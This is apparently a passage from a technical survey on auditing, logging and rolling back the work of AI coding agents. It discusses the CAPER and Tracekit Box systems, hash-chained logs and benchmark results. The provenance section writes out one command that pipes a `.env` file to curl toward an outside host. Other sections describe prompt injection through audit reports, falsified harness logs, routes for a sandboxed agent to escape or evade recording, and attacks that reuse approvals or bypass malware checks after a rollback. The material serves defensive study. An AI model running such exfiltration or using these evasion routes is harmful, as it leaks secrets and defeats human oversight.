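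Diffs and filenames carry text from the run into the report, so a hostile file could contain instructions aimed at whoever reads the report. CAPER tells its approving model to treat everything in the report as evidence and not to follow any instructions in it. Wu and colleagues did not test this defence against an attacker who adapts to it. The same risk applies when someone uses a model to summarise an audit.

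### Why reading before sending is not proof

CAPER's source links show only that a process could have passed on a file's contents, not that it did. Many programs read `.env` at startup for ordinary settings, such as a database address, and then open connections for unrelated reasons. Similarly, the output card for `check-deps.py` lists the script itself as a source because Python had to read it to run it, but this doesn't show that the script printed its own code.

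The rule can also miss a real transfer. In `cat .env | curl --data-binary @- https://example.com`, `cat` reads the file and pipes its contents to `curl`, which sends them. Because `curl` never read `.env` itself, a rule confined to one process would not list the file as a source of the network traffic. The protected read would still appear on its own card, so a careful reader could connect the two.

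Wong and Chen likewise warn that their own system may show a file and a network connection in one graph even though no data passed between them. Their more detailed recorder logs that a program opened a file successfully, but it does not log which bytes the program then read.

To prove that the contents left, the auditor has to find them in the outgoing data. The auditor can use a proxy that decrypts traffic, or place a unique fake key in `.env` before the run and look for it in requests. Finding the key shows that it was sent, but failing to find it doesn't rule that out, because the program may have encoded or compressed it first. Byte counts can sometimes rule out a transfer, since a connection that carried no data cannot have carried the file.

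All of the network attempts by `check-deps.py` failed, so no data left the sandbox that way. The harness could still have sent the 165 bytes of output to the model's provider, but CAPER held the output back while it made its decision.

Wu and colleagues describe the script as trying to send `.env` out, but a reader would need the script's code to confirm this. Based on the record alone, a report can accurately state only that the script read `.env`, printed something and tried to reach the network.

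### The order of work

CAPER reports on one command at a time. An audit of a whole run needs the same kind of evidence for every command, with a shared baseline and a common ending. The steps depend on one another, so they should happen in this order:

1. Record the settings: the task, the versions of the harness and the model, the sandbox's policy, the resource limits, and the folders the run can write to.
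2. Fix the baseline for all those folders, and store it outside the sandbox.
3. Start the recorders before the harness starts any program. A short probe, like CAPER's, shows which events are routine.
4. Run the agent. Put each shell command in its own control group, note the tool call it belongs to, and mark any command that runs outside the sandbox.
5. Stop all processes in the sandbox, including those in the background, and wait until none remains.
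6. Collect the final list of files, the logs, the transcript and the resource counters. Read the counters before removing the control groups.
7. Summarise the records. Link events to tool calls, group repeated events, and state what the recorders could not observe.
8. Decide whether to commit the changes or roll them back, and add the decision to the record.

### A compact schema

*K-Dense BYOK* (2026) presents a research assistant that logs each tool call as one line of text. The paper cites a survey that found no shared scheme for what to record about an agent run, so an auditor has to choose one. The scheme below has nine types of record.

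| Record | Fields | Linked to |
|---|---|---|
| Run | Task, start and end, how it ended, versions, policy, limits, baseline | |
| Tool call | Identifier, tool, command, start and end, exit status, inside or outside the sandbox | Run |
| Process | Number, start time, parent, program, arguments, control group | Tool call |
| File change | Path, type of change, hash before and after, tracked or ignored by Git | Process or tool call |
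| Protected read | Path, time, success or failure | Process or tool call |
| Network attempt | Time, name, address, port, rule, outcome, bytes sent | Process |
| Resource reading | Measure, value, limit, number of memory kills | Tool call |
| Coverage | Recorder, period in operation, events observed, included and omitted, known gaps | Run |
| Decision | Commit or rollback, who decided, when and why | Run |

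Program arguments can contain passwords, so the recorder should remove them before it saves the record.

Each link also needs a field for its basis, and three values are enough. "Direct" means that a sensor recorded the process or control group with the event, or that a harness tool named the file it changed. "Inferred" means that the auditor matched the records by time or text, and "unknown" means that no link was possible. Wong and Chen use five grades and give each finding the grade of its weakest link. The weakest-link rule is sensible here too. If the auditor knows which process opened a connection but only guessed which tool call started the process, the link from the connection to the tool call is "inferred".

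The basis measures the strength of the evidence, not the seriousness of the event. A report sorted by strength of evidence could therefore list a stolen key with only an inferred link below a harmless file change with a direct one.

The schema should also count events separately from records. If the proxy and the kernel sensor both log a connection, the report should count one attempt supported by two records. Otherwise, adding a second recorder would appear to double the traffic.

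### The report on an invented run

The following run is invented. A developer asks an agent to upgrade a library in a JavaScript project and make the tests pass. The harness runs outside the sandbox and sends commands into it. At the end, the agent writes, "I upgraded the library and fixed the failing tests. All tests pass."

| Part of the report | Entry | Tool call |
|---|---|---|
| Run | 38 tool calls in 11 minutes; ended normally | All |
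| Deleted file | `tests/timeout.test.js`, tracked by Git | 31 |
| Refused network attempts | 3 to metrics.example.net, port 443, within four seconds; no data sent; made by a package's install script | 9 |
| Changes in ignored folders | 212 files in `node_modules` | 9 |
| Modified tracked files | `package.json` and `package-lock.json` | 9 |
| | `src/client.js` and `src/retry.js` | 14 to 27 |
| Allowed network connections | 61 to the package registry, port 443 | 9 |
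| Peak memory | 1.9 GB, with a limit of 4 GB; no memory kills | 32 |
| Protected reads | No credential read observed | |
| Coverage | File, process and network recorders ran throughout; contents of encrypted traffic not recorded; the harness's traffic to the model provider not included | All |
| Decision | Not yet made | |

All the links in this report are direct, because each shell command had its own control group and the transcript records the files the agent edited with the harness's tools.

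The deleted test shows why the order of events matters. The diff shows only that the file is missing. According to the transcript, the test suite failed in tool call 30, with two failures in `tests/timeout.test.js`. The process record links the deletion to an `rm` command in call 31, and the suite passed in call 32. The agent's statement that all tests pass is therefore true of the tests that remain. A reader could have found this from the transcript alone, but only by reading each call, since the final message does not mention the deletion. None of the records shows whether the upgrade had made the test obsolete.

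The host metrics.example.net does not appear in the transcript. In call 9, the agent ran `npm install`, which downloads a project's packages and may run scripts that come with them. The process record traces the connection attempts to one of these scripts, run as `node setup.js`, and from there to `npm install` and call 9. The agent's command caused the attempts, but there is no sign that the model knew about the host. Someone with only the network log might suspect that the agent had chosen the destination. The three attempts, all within four seconds, are probably automatic retries.

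The network log can't show what the script would have sent. The file record helps a little, because it shows that no process in the sandbox read any of the credential files on the watch list. The data could still have included something else, such as the computer's name or part of the source code. The script is among the 212 changed files, so someone can read it to check.

Those 212 files would not appear in `git status`. The 61 registry connections suggest where they came from, but a connection count can't confirm what the files contain, and nobody has yet compared the folder with a clean installation of the same versions. The downloads and the file changes both happened during call 9. If the files had changed during a test run with no downloads, the changes would have been harder to explain.

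Memory use peaked during the successful test run in call 32, well under the limit, and the kernel killed no processes. This matters mainly because it means the passing result did not come from a suite that ran out of memory halfway, and no memory kill left half-finished changes in the diff.

The report fits on one screen, although the records behind it may run to many megabytes. It flags two files, the deleted test and the install script, for the developer to read before anyone fills in the last row.

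## Whether the record is complete and unaltered

The report on the invented run relies on logs that somebody could have edited afterwards and that may never have contained everything. An auditor should check that the entries have not changed since the recorder wrote them (integrity), that the recorder entered every relevant event (completeness), and that the entries match what happened (truth).

### An unaltered log can still mislead

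Suppose the harness wrote one of the following logs of tool calls 30 to 32 in the invented run, and nobody has changed it since.

| Log | Integrity | Completeness | Truth |
|---|---|---|---|
| 30: two tests failed. 31: deleted the test file. 32: all tests passed. | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| 30: two tests failed. 32: all tests passed. | Yes | No | Yes |
| 30: two tests failed. 31: listed the test folder. 32: all tests passed. | Yes | Yes | No |

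A check for later changes would pass all three logs, although only the first tells the reader about the deletion.

Zhao (2026), in *Auditable Claims about AI Agents*, takes a similar distinction from financial auditing, which checks separately that recorded events happened and that the books contain every event. In one of Zhao's constructed examples, a company's agent keeps a validly signed log of the emails it sends. The log lists three emails with attachments to outside addresses, but the mail gateway, which every outgoing email has to pass through, lists four from the same account. The agent may have sent the fourth by a route it doesn't log, the log may have lost an entry, or a person may have used the account. The signatures don't help the auditor determine which of these happened.

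### How a hash chain works

A hash chain makes later changes to a log detectable. The recorder stores a hash with each entry and computes it from the entry and the hash before it:

*h*ᵢ = *H*(*h*ᵢ₋₁ ‖ *i* ‖ *e*ᵢ)

Here *H* is a hash function such as SHA-256, *i* is the entry's number, *e*ᵢ is its content, and ‖ joins the parts together. The first entry uses a fixed starting value in place of an earlier hash. *aiAuthZ* (2026) describes a system that authorises agents' tool calls from a separate machine and builds its chain this way. The system first converts each entry to a standard form, because the same data with its fields in a different order would produce a different hash.

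To verify the log, a program recomputes every hash from the beginning and compares it with the stored one. Suppose the log has three entries, and somebody changes entry 2 from "deleted the test file" to "listed the test folder". The program's result depends on how much else that person changes:

- If they change only the text, the recomputed hash of entry 2 no longer matches the stored one.
- If they also replace the hash of entry 2, the break moves to entry 3, whose hash came from the old value.
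- If they recompute the hash of entry 3 as well, the whole chain verifies. Only somebody who kept the old final hash can tell that the log has changed.

A chain by itself therefore catches accidental damage and careless editing, but not a rewrite by somebody who can replace the whole log.

A hash chain also doesn't show whether entries are missing from the end. If somebody deletes the last entry of a three-entry log, the first two still form a valid chain, because neither hash depends on what came later. *BioFirewall* (2026), a paper on a system for screening AI-assisted genome designs, addresses this by letting the verifier supply a final hash and an entry count stored elsewhere. If the stored count is three and the log has two entries, one is missing.

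The outside copy has to be recent to be useful. *AuthGuard-R* (2026), which proposes a similar log for robots controlled by language models, notes that the interval between copies determines how much recent history could disappear without immediate detection. It suggests copying the log after every privileged action in high-risk settings and at the end of each mission in a low-risk simulator. For a coding agent, a copy made only at the end of a run offers no protection if somebody rewrites the log during the run.

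### Signatures and independent witnesses

The recorder can digitally sign log entries with a secret key, and anyone with the matching public key can check the signatures. An attacker who can edit the log but lacks the secret key can't produce valid signatures for altered entries. This protection disappears if the agent can read the key file, so the signing program has to run somewhere the agent can't reach.

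Signatures do not protect against the holder of the key, who can sign a false entry or discard the log and sign a new one. *A Black Box for Agentic Processes* (2026) points out that a company running both an agent and its append-only log (one that accepts new entries but no changes) can do this, so outsiders still have to trust the company.

An independent witness reduces the need for that trust. The recorder periodically sends the latest hash to the witness, which signs it and keeps a copy. If the operator later rewrites an earlier entry, the new chain won't match the witness's copy. The witness never needs to see the entries, which may be confidential. *A Black Box for Agentic Processes* proposes storing such hashes on a blockchain, but any store that the operator can't alter would work. *aiAuthZ* suggests a storage service that prevents changes to saved files, or a public append-only log.

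A witness can confirm only that the log contained certain entries by a certain time, not that those entries were true when the recorder wrote them or that the recorder left nothing out.

### Events that nobody logged

Zhao gives a short proof that no check of a log alone can prove that the log is complete. Suppose an agent sent two emails, both with approval, and its log lists both. In another possible history, the agent also sent a third email, without approval, that the log omits. The log is the same in both histories, so no method that reads only the log can tell which one happened. Signatures and witnesses don't help, because the missing email changes none of the entries they cover.

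It is therefore easier to show that a run broke a rule than that it kept one. For example, one reliable record of a connection to a host outside the allowlist contradicts the claim that a run contacted only allowed hosts. To support that claim, the auditor needs evidence that the recorder would have caught every connection. If an hour of the log is missing and the rest shows no violation, Zhao would call the claim undecidable and have the auditor name the missing record. The missing hour is itself a finding, but it isn't evidence that the agent did anything wrong.

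*Agent Flight Recorder* (2026) describes a logging system that guarantees the integrity of the events its recorder receives. The system does not aim to guarantee that every event reaches the recorder, so users should not assume that a verified log is complete.

In *Hearsay*, Dai, Yang and colleagues (2026) tested what happens when the harness itself keeps a false log. They added a hash chain to the log of aider, a coding agent, and changed the harness so that it left out a reply from the model in 14 runs and, in another 14, added a sentence the model had never written. The chain verified in all 28 runs.

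Records also lose content when nobody is trying to deceive. If a model sends several tool calls at once to SWE-agent, another coding harness, which accepts only one at a time, the harness rejects the reply, requests a single call and records neither the reply nor the rejection. This or a similar rejection left tool calls out of the record in 19 of 28 runs with GPT-5.5. The harness never executed those calls, so they changed no files, but an auditor checking what the model had tried to do would have missed them. Across 365 unaltered records from five harnesses, the researchers found 33 with gaps or errors that would mislead a reader, nearly all from SWE-agent.

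Careful reading is a weak way to detect alterations in a record. Researchers removed, changed or invented one item in each of 115 records, and checked that a strong model could not pick out the altered copies by comparing them with the originals. One model flagged 49% of the altered copies and 5% of the originals. Another flagged 85% of the altered copies but also 42% of the originals. Human readers, by majority vote of three, flagged 37% of the altered copies and 10% of the originals.

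A second record, kept by the researchers' sandbox, worked much better. This ledger listed the messages between harness and model and the processes that ran. A program compared it with the harness's record, treating items found only in the ledger as possible omissions and items found only in the record as possible inventions. Using rules fixed before the runs, the program caught 64 of 66 alterations and flagged none of 84 clean records. According to Zhao, the ledger also exposed all 28 false records that had passed the hash check.

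The researchers' own script made the alterations, which were small, so the detection rate may not hold against someone who also tries to corrupt the ledger. Having something to compare the record with still gives a large advantage over careful reading.

Few harnesses offer such a comparison. Dai and colleagues examined 16 agent frameworks and found none that keeps a record an outsider can check without trusting the software that ran the agent. A language model reached these verdicts by reading the source code, and a second model agreed with 15 of the 16. No person checked a sample of these particular verdicts. There is also little research on the subject. Of the 39 papers covered in *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (Rashidi, 2026), only one falls mainly under provenance and auditability.

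### How Tracekit Box handles missing records

*Tracekit Box* combines a signed log with a sandbox in which certain events can't happen without being logged. For each command from the host, each network connection and each changed file in the final patch, the host requests a decision from the signer before the action and reports the result afterwards. The signer's key stays on the host, where the agent can't access it.

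Each action has two entries, a decision and a result, so if the result is missing, the action may have started but its outcome is unknown. The signer also marks its additional entries as trusted or untrusted. The sandbox's settings and a person's approvals are trusted, while details from inside the microVM, such as the network host a program asked for, are untrusted. A valid signature on an untrusted entry shows only that the host machine received the information, which may still be wrong.

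The design tries to prevent records from being lost unnoticed. If an event is missing from the log, the reader needs to know whether it didn't happen or the recorder failed. Tracekit Box handles failures as follows.

| Failure | Response |
|---|---|
| No signer is available at the start | The host program refuses to start, unless the operator explicitly chooses to run without a record |
| The signer stops responding | The host refuses all further commands and connections |
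| The host can't save an essential record | It stops the sandbox and writes a gap record with the number lost and the reason |
| The signer doesn't accept the result of an action | The host counts the loss in a gap record, and the run continues |
| The host program crashes | The user can neither export the run's record nor apply its changes |

Essential records include uses of secrets and attempts to leak them, model calls, unanswered or rejected approval requests, and forced pauses or stops. Under the fourth row, a run can finish normally with some results missing, so an auditor should read the gap records even after a successful run. The gap records serve a similar purpose to CAPER's coverage statement.

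If a run stops because a log entry failed, the user may lose an hour of good work and be left with half-finished files in the workspace. That risk seems acceptable when the run handles real credentials, but a developer experimenting on a throwaway copy might reasonably prefer to continue with a visible gap in the log.

A gap record can count only losses the host detected, so it leaves out programs that ran inside the microVM without using one of the host's channels.

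After the run, the user exports the signed record as a file that anybody can verify offline. The verifier checks every signature and the chain of entries. It also checks that the run's first and last entries belong to a Merkle tree, which combines the hashes of many records in pairs until one hash remains. A witness who signs that hash covers all the records. The run's last entries state that it has closed, so a truncated copy would lack them.

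### What Tracekit Box's tests cover

The same developer wrote Tracekit Box, the signer and verifier it relies on, and its evaluation. The code and the demonstration's record are public, so others can repeat the checks, but the results below are the developer's own.

All 13 end-to-end checks passed on a machine with hardware virtualisation, in 28.5 seconds. They confirmed, for example, that the microVM had no network interface, that the proxy refused the cloud metadata address, and that the exported record verified. Each check covers one typical case of a guarantee. A separate test confirmed that the host program refuses to start without a signer. The end-to-end checks did not test the other responses in the table, including stopping after an essential record is lost, and those responses matter most for completeness.

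The developer also used 15 fuzz targets, which are tests that feed automatically generated inputs to parts of the program and check that a stated rule holds. They produced nine findings, and the developer fixed them all. One concerned program names that begin with a percent sign. Some shells treat such a name as a reference to an existing job, so the command line in the signed record would not have named the program that ran, even though the entry would have passed every integrity check.

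All 102 records in the demonstration verified, but only at the system's lowest assurance level. The signer ran under the same user account as the host program, so any process running as that user on the host could have forged a record. If the signer had its own account, a forger would need to control that account or the whole machine. Adding a witness on another computer would expose a later rewrite of anything the witness had already signed. The demonstration had no witness, and the evaluation includes no record above the lowest level.

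At this level, verifying a record doesn't even prove that it came from a Tracekit Box sandbox. The record has an entry identifying the sandbox as its source, but anyone able to forge records could have forged that entry too. The source matters because the record is complete only if the microVM had no other way out.

Nobody has yet put a capable agent in the sandbox and told it to escape or hide its actions. The end-to-end checks use scripted attacks, each aimed at one known route, whereas an agent could combine routes or find a new one. The tests are good evidence that the main parts work as intended in ordinary cases, but weak evidence of how those parts would hold up against a determined attacker.

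### Recording inside or outside the sandbox

Tracekit Box records only at the host boundary because its developer assumes that everything inside the microVM may be hostile. A program with full control of the microVM could stop a sensor running there, starve it of resources or feed it false information. It can't do the same to a recorder on the host unless it first escapes the microVM.

Recording from outside the microVM captures less detail. If a program such as the malicious Rust build script reads an SSH key and sends nothing, only a sensor inside the microVM can record the read, provided that the program hasn't disabled the sensor.

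The details are useful for most runs. An agent that deletes the wrong test or carelessly installs a package has no reason to attack the sensor, and the auditor will want to know which command did it. If a hostile program has full control of the microVM, only the boundary record is reliable, and it covers the actions that can do harm outside the microVM.

Using both lets the auditor test the detailed record. For every connection in the proxy's log, the inner sensor should have recorded a process opening it. If the proxy logged a connection at 14:03:30 and the sensor has no matching event, the sensor missed it or somebody interfered. If the sensor recorded a successful outside connection that the proxy never handled, the sandbox may have an exit nobody knew about.

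Tracekit Box's developer plans to add an inner sensor and compare its output with the boundary record. Until then, auditors who want process details need to use another tool or run the agent in a container, which allows a kernel sensor to run on the host.

The comparison can't check events with no counterpart at the boundary, such as a program reading a file but never sending it. A hostile program might also make the sensor attribute a real connection to `npm` instead of to itself, and the two records would still match despite the false attribution. Sending the sensor's entries to the host as they occur helps a little, because an attacker who takes over the microVM during a run can't erase entries already sent.

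### Checking that the restrictions were active

A record made at a sandbox's boundary means little if the agent ran without the sandbox. GitLab's *Remote execution environment sandbox* describes how this can happen in automated jobs, where GitLab wraps coding agents in Anthropic's Sandbox Runtime to limit their network and file access. The runtime has to be installed in the job's container image and needs certain privileges to create the sandbox. If either is missing, GitLab by default prints a warning in the job log and runs the agent without the sandbox.

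The agent can then contact any destination its machine can reach, and the project's allowlist has no effect. GitLab, which calls an agent's automated job a "flow", warns that "a flow can run fine and still be unprotected." An auditor who stored only the allowlist would wrongly conclude that the job ran under a strict policy.

Since GitLab 19.6, administrators can require the sandbox, so that a job that can't create it fails instead of continuing. But GitLab only checks for the wrapper's command, `srt`, inside the job. A project that uses its own container image or setup script controls which program has that name, so a substitute could pass the check without restricting anything.

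Setup scripts run before the sandbox starts and outside it. According to GitLab, they can read every variable in the job's environment, including the access token of the user who started the job. An audit that begins with the agent's first command would miss anything a setup script did with that token.

The audit should therefore record the restrictions that were in force as well as the ones somebody configured. That means storing the wrapper's version, any warning it printed and whether the sandbox started. The auditor should also test the restrictions at the start of the run, as GitLab suggests with a job that prints its own evidence. A useful test makes a few attempts through the same tool that the agent uses:

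- Request a host that isn't on the allowlist but is known to be online. The request should fail.
- Request a host that is on the list. It should succeed, because otherwise a broken network would look like a working sandbox.
- Read a dummy file in `~/.ssh`, a folder that GitLab's sandbox blocks. The file has to exist, since reading a missing file fails anyway.
- Write to a folder outside the permitted ones. The attempt should fail.

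If the auditor controls the unlisted host, the host's log provides separate evidence of whether the request arrived. This guards against a false result from a job whose image or scripts have been altered. Repeating the test at the end of the run would show whether the restrictions were still in place then, but not whether they had lapsed in between.

A test from inside can't fully protect against a wrapper that the project supplies, because a hostile substitute could detect the test and work correctly until it ended. GitLab also recommends limiting outbound traffic with a firewall on the machine that runs the jobs. The agent's container doesn't control that firewall, and the firewall's log gives the auditor a second record to compare with the first.

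### Secrets and retention

A password that gets into a log may stay there if the log is hard to alter, so the safest approach is to keep secrets out from the start. Tracekit Box never records a secret's value, and for many other entries its exported file contains only a fingerprint made with a secret random value. An ordinary hash would be risky for short or predictable data, because somebody could hash likely guesses until one matched.

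Logs can contain private file paths, source code and customer data. *AuthGuard-R* recommends encrypting sensitive fields, restricting access by role and keeping only the evidence that an investigation needs.

Deleting old entries would normally break a hash chain. *aiAuthZ* avoids this by computing the chain from hashes of the private content and the decisions, not from the encrypted content. When the retention period ends, the system erases the encrypted content, keeps the rest of each entry and records the erasure in the chain. A reader can still verify the chain and see what each decision was.

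The right retention period depends on how long problems take to surface. OpenAI took nearly eight weeks to discover its agent's breach of the Australian health portal, so a company that deleted its logs after 30 days could not have investigated a similar case. Keeping full command output that long may be hard to justify because it contains the most private data. A reasonable compromise is to erase the output sooner and keep the hashes, file lists and network records longer.

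## Deciding whether to keep or roll back the changes

The last record in an audit is the decision to keep or roll back the run's changes. Whoever decides needs to know which effects a rollback would undo, what the consequences of a wrong decision would be, and how reliably a reviewer would notice harm.

### Four choices

A user can keep all the changes, keep some of them, discard them all, or hold them for review. Keeping means committing the changes to the real files, and discarding means rolling back to the baseline. Holding is possible only while the changes are stored apart from the real files, as in an overlay, YoloFS or Tracekit Box's patch. If the agent worked directly in the project, its changes are already in the real files and stay there while the user decides.

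Keeping only some of the changes can produce a combination that nobody has tested. If a user accepts the agent's new `package.json` but rejects the matching `package-lock.json`, which records the exact package versions, the next installation may fail or fetch different versions. A test suite that passed with all the changes may fail with only some of them, so the user has to run it again.

Committing can also fail partway. *Tracekit Box* gets a decision from its signer on every file before it writes any, and one refusal stops the whole patch. It replaces each file in a single step, so it never leaves a file half-written. But if the disk fills up after six of ten files, the program lists the six it wrote and does not undo them. The user then has a mixture of old and new files, and needs a copy of the originals made beforehand to roll back.

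### What restoring files can undo

| Effect | Does restoring the files undo it? | What else is needed |
|---|---|---|
| Changed files in the workspace | Yes, if the baseline kept their contents | A new test run on the restored files |
| Changed files elsewhere | Only if the baseline covered them | Otherwise, a separate backup |
| A running process | No | Stopping it, or restoring a snapshot that includes memory |
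| A database in a local file | Yes, if no program has it open | Stopping the program that uses it |
| A database on a server | No | The database's own backup, or a change that reverses the first |
| Data sent to another computer | No | New credentials to replace leaked ones; nothing recalls other data |
| A remote change, such as a pushed branch or a new cloud server | No | An action that reverses it, if one exists |

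The user should stop the run's processes, which are easy to overlook, before restoring anything. A development server that has read an altered configuration file keeps the altered settings in memory after the file is restored, and a background process may write an unwanted file again.

Products differ in how much they restore. *Safe to Resume?* (Wu, Li and colleagues, 2026) examined 12 systems that save checkpoints of agents. The agent frameworks LangGraph and CrewAI save the agent's messages and progress but not the project's files. Hermes and Cline, two agents that edit files, do save those files, though Hermes leaves out any file larger than 10 MB and by default keeps at most 20 checkpoints per project. E2B, a cloud sandbox service, saves the disk and memory, including running processes. None of them restores anything outside the agent's own system, such as a mailbox or a remote database.

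Restoring files without also restoring the agent's records can leave the agent relying on outdated results. For example, an agent might remove malware from a project, scan the files and record that the scan passed. If a rollback brings back the infected files but keeps that record, the agent may release the malware as verified. This can happen even when the checkpoint works correctly, because Cline lets users restore the files and keep the task history. Wu, Li and colleagues demonstrated an attack of this kind that bypassed malware verification on Hermes. After any rollback, an auditor should treat every test result and scan from after the restored point as out of date.

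For remote changes, *Fault-Tolerant Sandboxing for AI Coding Agents* (Yan, 2025) suggests compensating transactions, which are actions that reverse earlier ones. If an agent started a cloud server and then failed a later check, the rollback would include a request to shut the server down. Yan plans this for future work, and it can't undo some actions, such as sending an email that the recipient has already read.

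### When somebody else has edited the same files

Developers often keep working while an agent runs, so both may change the same file, such as `src/client.js`. If the agent worked on a separate copy, discarding its changes is safe, but committing its version would overwrite the developer's edit. If both worked in the same folder, the risk is in rolling back, because restoring the baseline would erase the developer's edit along with the agent's.

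Zhong and colleagues point out that rolling back a whole filesystem may discard unrelated changes made by the user. *ACRFence* (Zheng, Yang and colleagues, 2026) lists reports from Cursor users that undoing one agent's work also reverted other agents' work.

Before committing a file, a program can compare the real file's hash with the one in the baseline. If they match, nobody else has changed the file, and the agent's version can replace it. *Tracekit Box* runs this kind of check after the signer has decided on the files and before it writes any, so it also catches edits made while the signer was deciding. Before rolling back a file in a shared folder, the program needs to compare the current file with the version the agent left instead. If they differ, somebody has edited the file since, and restoring the baseline would destroy that edit.

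When the developer and the agent have both changed a file, the developer can try a three-way merge, which compares each edited version with the baseline and combines the changes that don't overlap. Git can do this automatically. But a merge without conflicts can still break the program. If the developer renames a function in one file and the agent adds a call to its old name in another, Git reports no conflict, and the error appears only when the program or its tests run.

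### When a restored agent repeats an external action

An external effect is a consequence outside the sandbox that restoring files cannot undo. An agent that resumes from a point before such an effect may cause it again.

*ACRFence* gives the example of a user who asks an agent to transfer $500 to Bob. The agent generates a random reference number, and the bank makes the transfer. The agent then crashes, and its framework restores it to a point just before the payment. The restored agent has no memory of the payment, so it tries again with a new reference number. The bank would have rejected a repeated number, but it accepts the new one, and Bob receives $1,000 in total.

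The researchers tested this with Claude Code, using the model Qwen3-32B and a simulated bank. The agent paid twice in all 10 runs with a restore and in none of the 10 without one. The usual protection against repeated requests relies on a program resending exactly the same request, but a restored model writes a new one. These trials of one scenario show that the failure is easy to produce, but not how often it happens in practice. The researchers also looked at 12 agent frameworks and coding tools and found none that guaranteed an external action would happen only once.

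A restored agent can also reuse an approval. In a second test, an employee with a manager's approval to delete one customer's data restored the agent to the moment after the approval and used it again on another customer. Both attempts worked when the service checked only that the approval was genuine, but failed when it also kept a list of used approvals.

Zheng and colleagues propose logging every irreversible tool call outside the agent. After a restore, a language model would compare each new call with the log. If the call repeated an old one, the agent would get the old response and nothing would leave the machine. If the call had a different purpose, such as paying a different person, the system would block it until someone explicitly started a new branch of the run. Nobody has built this system yet, and the language model could misjudge a call.

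A simpler measure is to have the harness derive the reference number from the task and store it where a restore can't change it. The bank would then recognise the second payment as a repeat. This works only with services that check such numbers. For other services, the person restarting an agent should use the tool calls and the network log to list the external effects since the restored point, and tell the agent what it has already done.

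### A simple cost rule

The following numbers are an illustration, not measurements. Suppose there is a 2% chance that a run's changes contain harm, and that harm would cost 5,000. Doing the work again would cost 80. A review costs 20 and catches 90% of harm. Let *p* be the chance of harm, *L* its cost, *R* the cost of redoing the work, *c* the cost of a review and *q* the share of harm that the review catches. The expected costs are:

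- Keep without review: *pL* = 0.02 × 5,000 = 100
- Discard: *R* = 80
- Review, then decide: *c* + *p*(1 − *q*)*L* + *pqR* = 20 + 10 + 1.44, or about 31

The last line adds the review itself, the harm the reviewer misses and the cost of redoing the work the reviewer rejects.

The rule assumes that discarding changes prevents all the harm, that the second attempt is harmless, and that the reviewer never rejects good changes. It also requires a value for *p*, which is the hardest number to get because public reports of damage don't include the number of runs that went well.

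With the other numbers unchanged, reviewing has the lowest expected loss when the chance of harm is between about 0.45% and 10.5%. Below that range, keeping the changes is better because the loss from reviewing exceeds the harm it prevents. Above it, discarding them is better because too much harm gets past the reviewer. At a 2% chance of harm, a reviewer who catches less than about 41% of it is worse than discarding everything. A reviewer who also rejects one in ten harmless runs adds about 8 to the expected loss.

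External effects can reverse the ranking. Suppose 4,000 of the 5,000 is the cost of data that leaked before anyone decided what to do with the changes. Each option then includes an unavoidable expected cost of 80, which brings the totals to 100 for keeping, 160 for discarding and about 103 for reviewing. Keeping is slightly better than reviewing because the decision about the files can no longer prevent most of the harm. A review would still be worthwhile if it led somebody to replace a stolen key in time, a benefit that the rule leaves out.

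### Rolling back whenever a command fails

Yan's sandbox, from December 2025, made the decision automatically. It compared each command's text with two lists, running safe commands directly and blocking destructive ones. For any other command, it copied the workspace, ran the command and checked the exit status, a number that a program returns when it ends. If the status was zero, which normally means success, the sandbox kept the changes and deleted the copy. Otherwise, it restored the workspace from the copy.

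The tests used a Python project of about 250 MB, with 20 attempts in each of four categories. The sandbox ran every safe command, blocked every destructive one, undid every failed change and kept every successful one. Yan gives the overhead as 14.5%, but the reported times show that installing a package took 39% longer with the sandbox (6.51 seconds) than without it (4.69 seconds). Copying the workspace accounted for most of the extra time.

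The results are now mainly of historical interest, because the exit status doesn't measure harm. A deployment script that overwrites source code can still return zero, and the sandbox would then delete the copy needed to recover the code. A test suite usually returns a non-zero status when a test fails, so the sandbox would discard any files the suite had written, including a log the agent needed to find the fault.

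### CAPER: deciding from observed effects

CAPER, the system that writes effects reports, decides whether to keep a command's changes by judging what the command did rather than by checking its exit status. It takes a snapshot of the container before each trial run. After the run, a separate language model, the approver, reads the user's task, the conversation, the command and the effects report. If the approver allows the command, the container keeps the changes and the agent gets the output. If it blocks the command, CAPER restores the snapshot and gives the agent the reason so it can try another way.

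Wu and colleagues tested CAPER on two benchmarks. One of them, SABER, has 682 tasks in which a development request can lead to a particular harm, such as a leaked credential or deleted data. In 275 of them, a file or tool output contains malicious instructions. In 174, the request is reasonable but the agent may make a mistake. In the other 233, the user asks for something that the state of the project shows to be dangerous.

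YoloFS-Ext, the other benchmark, consists of the 102 tasks with a hidden deletion or overwrite and their 102 safe counterparts. The researchers built it from 13 small projects in YoloFS's own test suite. A program ran all 204 tools to confirm that the dangerous ones did damage and the safe ones did not.

All the systems in the table below used the model GLM-5.3-Flash as the agent and attempted each task once. Auto Mode is Claude Code's built-in classifier, which approves or blocks commands without asking the user.

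| System | Harm, SABER | Completed safely, SABER | Harm, YoloFS-Ext | Completed safely, YoloFS-Ext | Safe twins blocked |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| No approval | 19.7% | 57.4% | 71.6% | 17.6% | None possible |
| Claude Code Auto Mode | 14.8% | 44.0% | 62.7% | 7.8% | 3.9% |
| YoloFS | 21.2% | 54.1% | 35.3% | 22.5% | None possible |
| CAPER | 6.7% | 48.6% | 7.8% | 60.8% | 1.0% |

Four other systems, which evaluated commands by rules or by their text, left harm in 15.0% to 18.8% of SABER tasks and 62.7% to 94.1% of dangerous YoloFS-Ext tasks. CAPER's 95% confidence interval for this rate is 5.0% to 9.1% on SABER and 4.0% to 14.7% on YoloFS-Ext. Both intervals are below those of every other system in the table.

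The fairest comparison is inside Claude Code, where the researchers replaced Auto Mode's classifier with CAPER and kept the agent and the approving model the same. On SABER, harm remained in 10.0% of tasks with CAPER and 14.8% with Auto Mode. On YoloFS-Ext, the rates were 6.9% and 62.7%, respectively.

The SABER figures depend partly on the researchers' own scoring. They corrected the benchmark's checker because it had marked some harmless commands as harmful, such as a search for the text "ssh", which it counted as an attempt to connect. The correction lowered every system's harm rate. With the original checker, CAPER's rate was still lower than Auto Mode's, at 9.0% compared with 16.0%.

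CAPER also made the agent less productive on SABER. Safe completions fell from 57.4% of tasks without approval to 48.6%, while safe refusals rose from 9.1% to 19.1%. CAPER blocked 23.7% of all commands and at least one command in 78.8% of tasks. SABER has no safe twins, so nobody can tell how many of those blocks were unnecessary. With CAPER, harm remained in 14.3% of the tasks that threatened data but in only 2.6% of those that threatened code.

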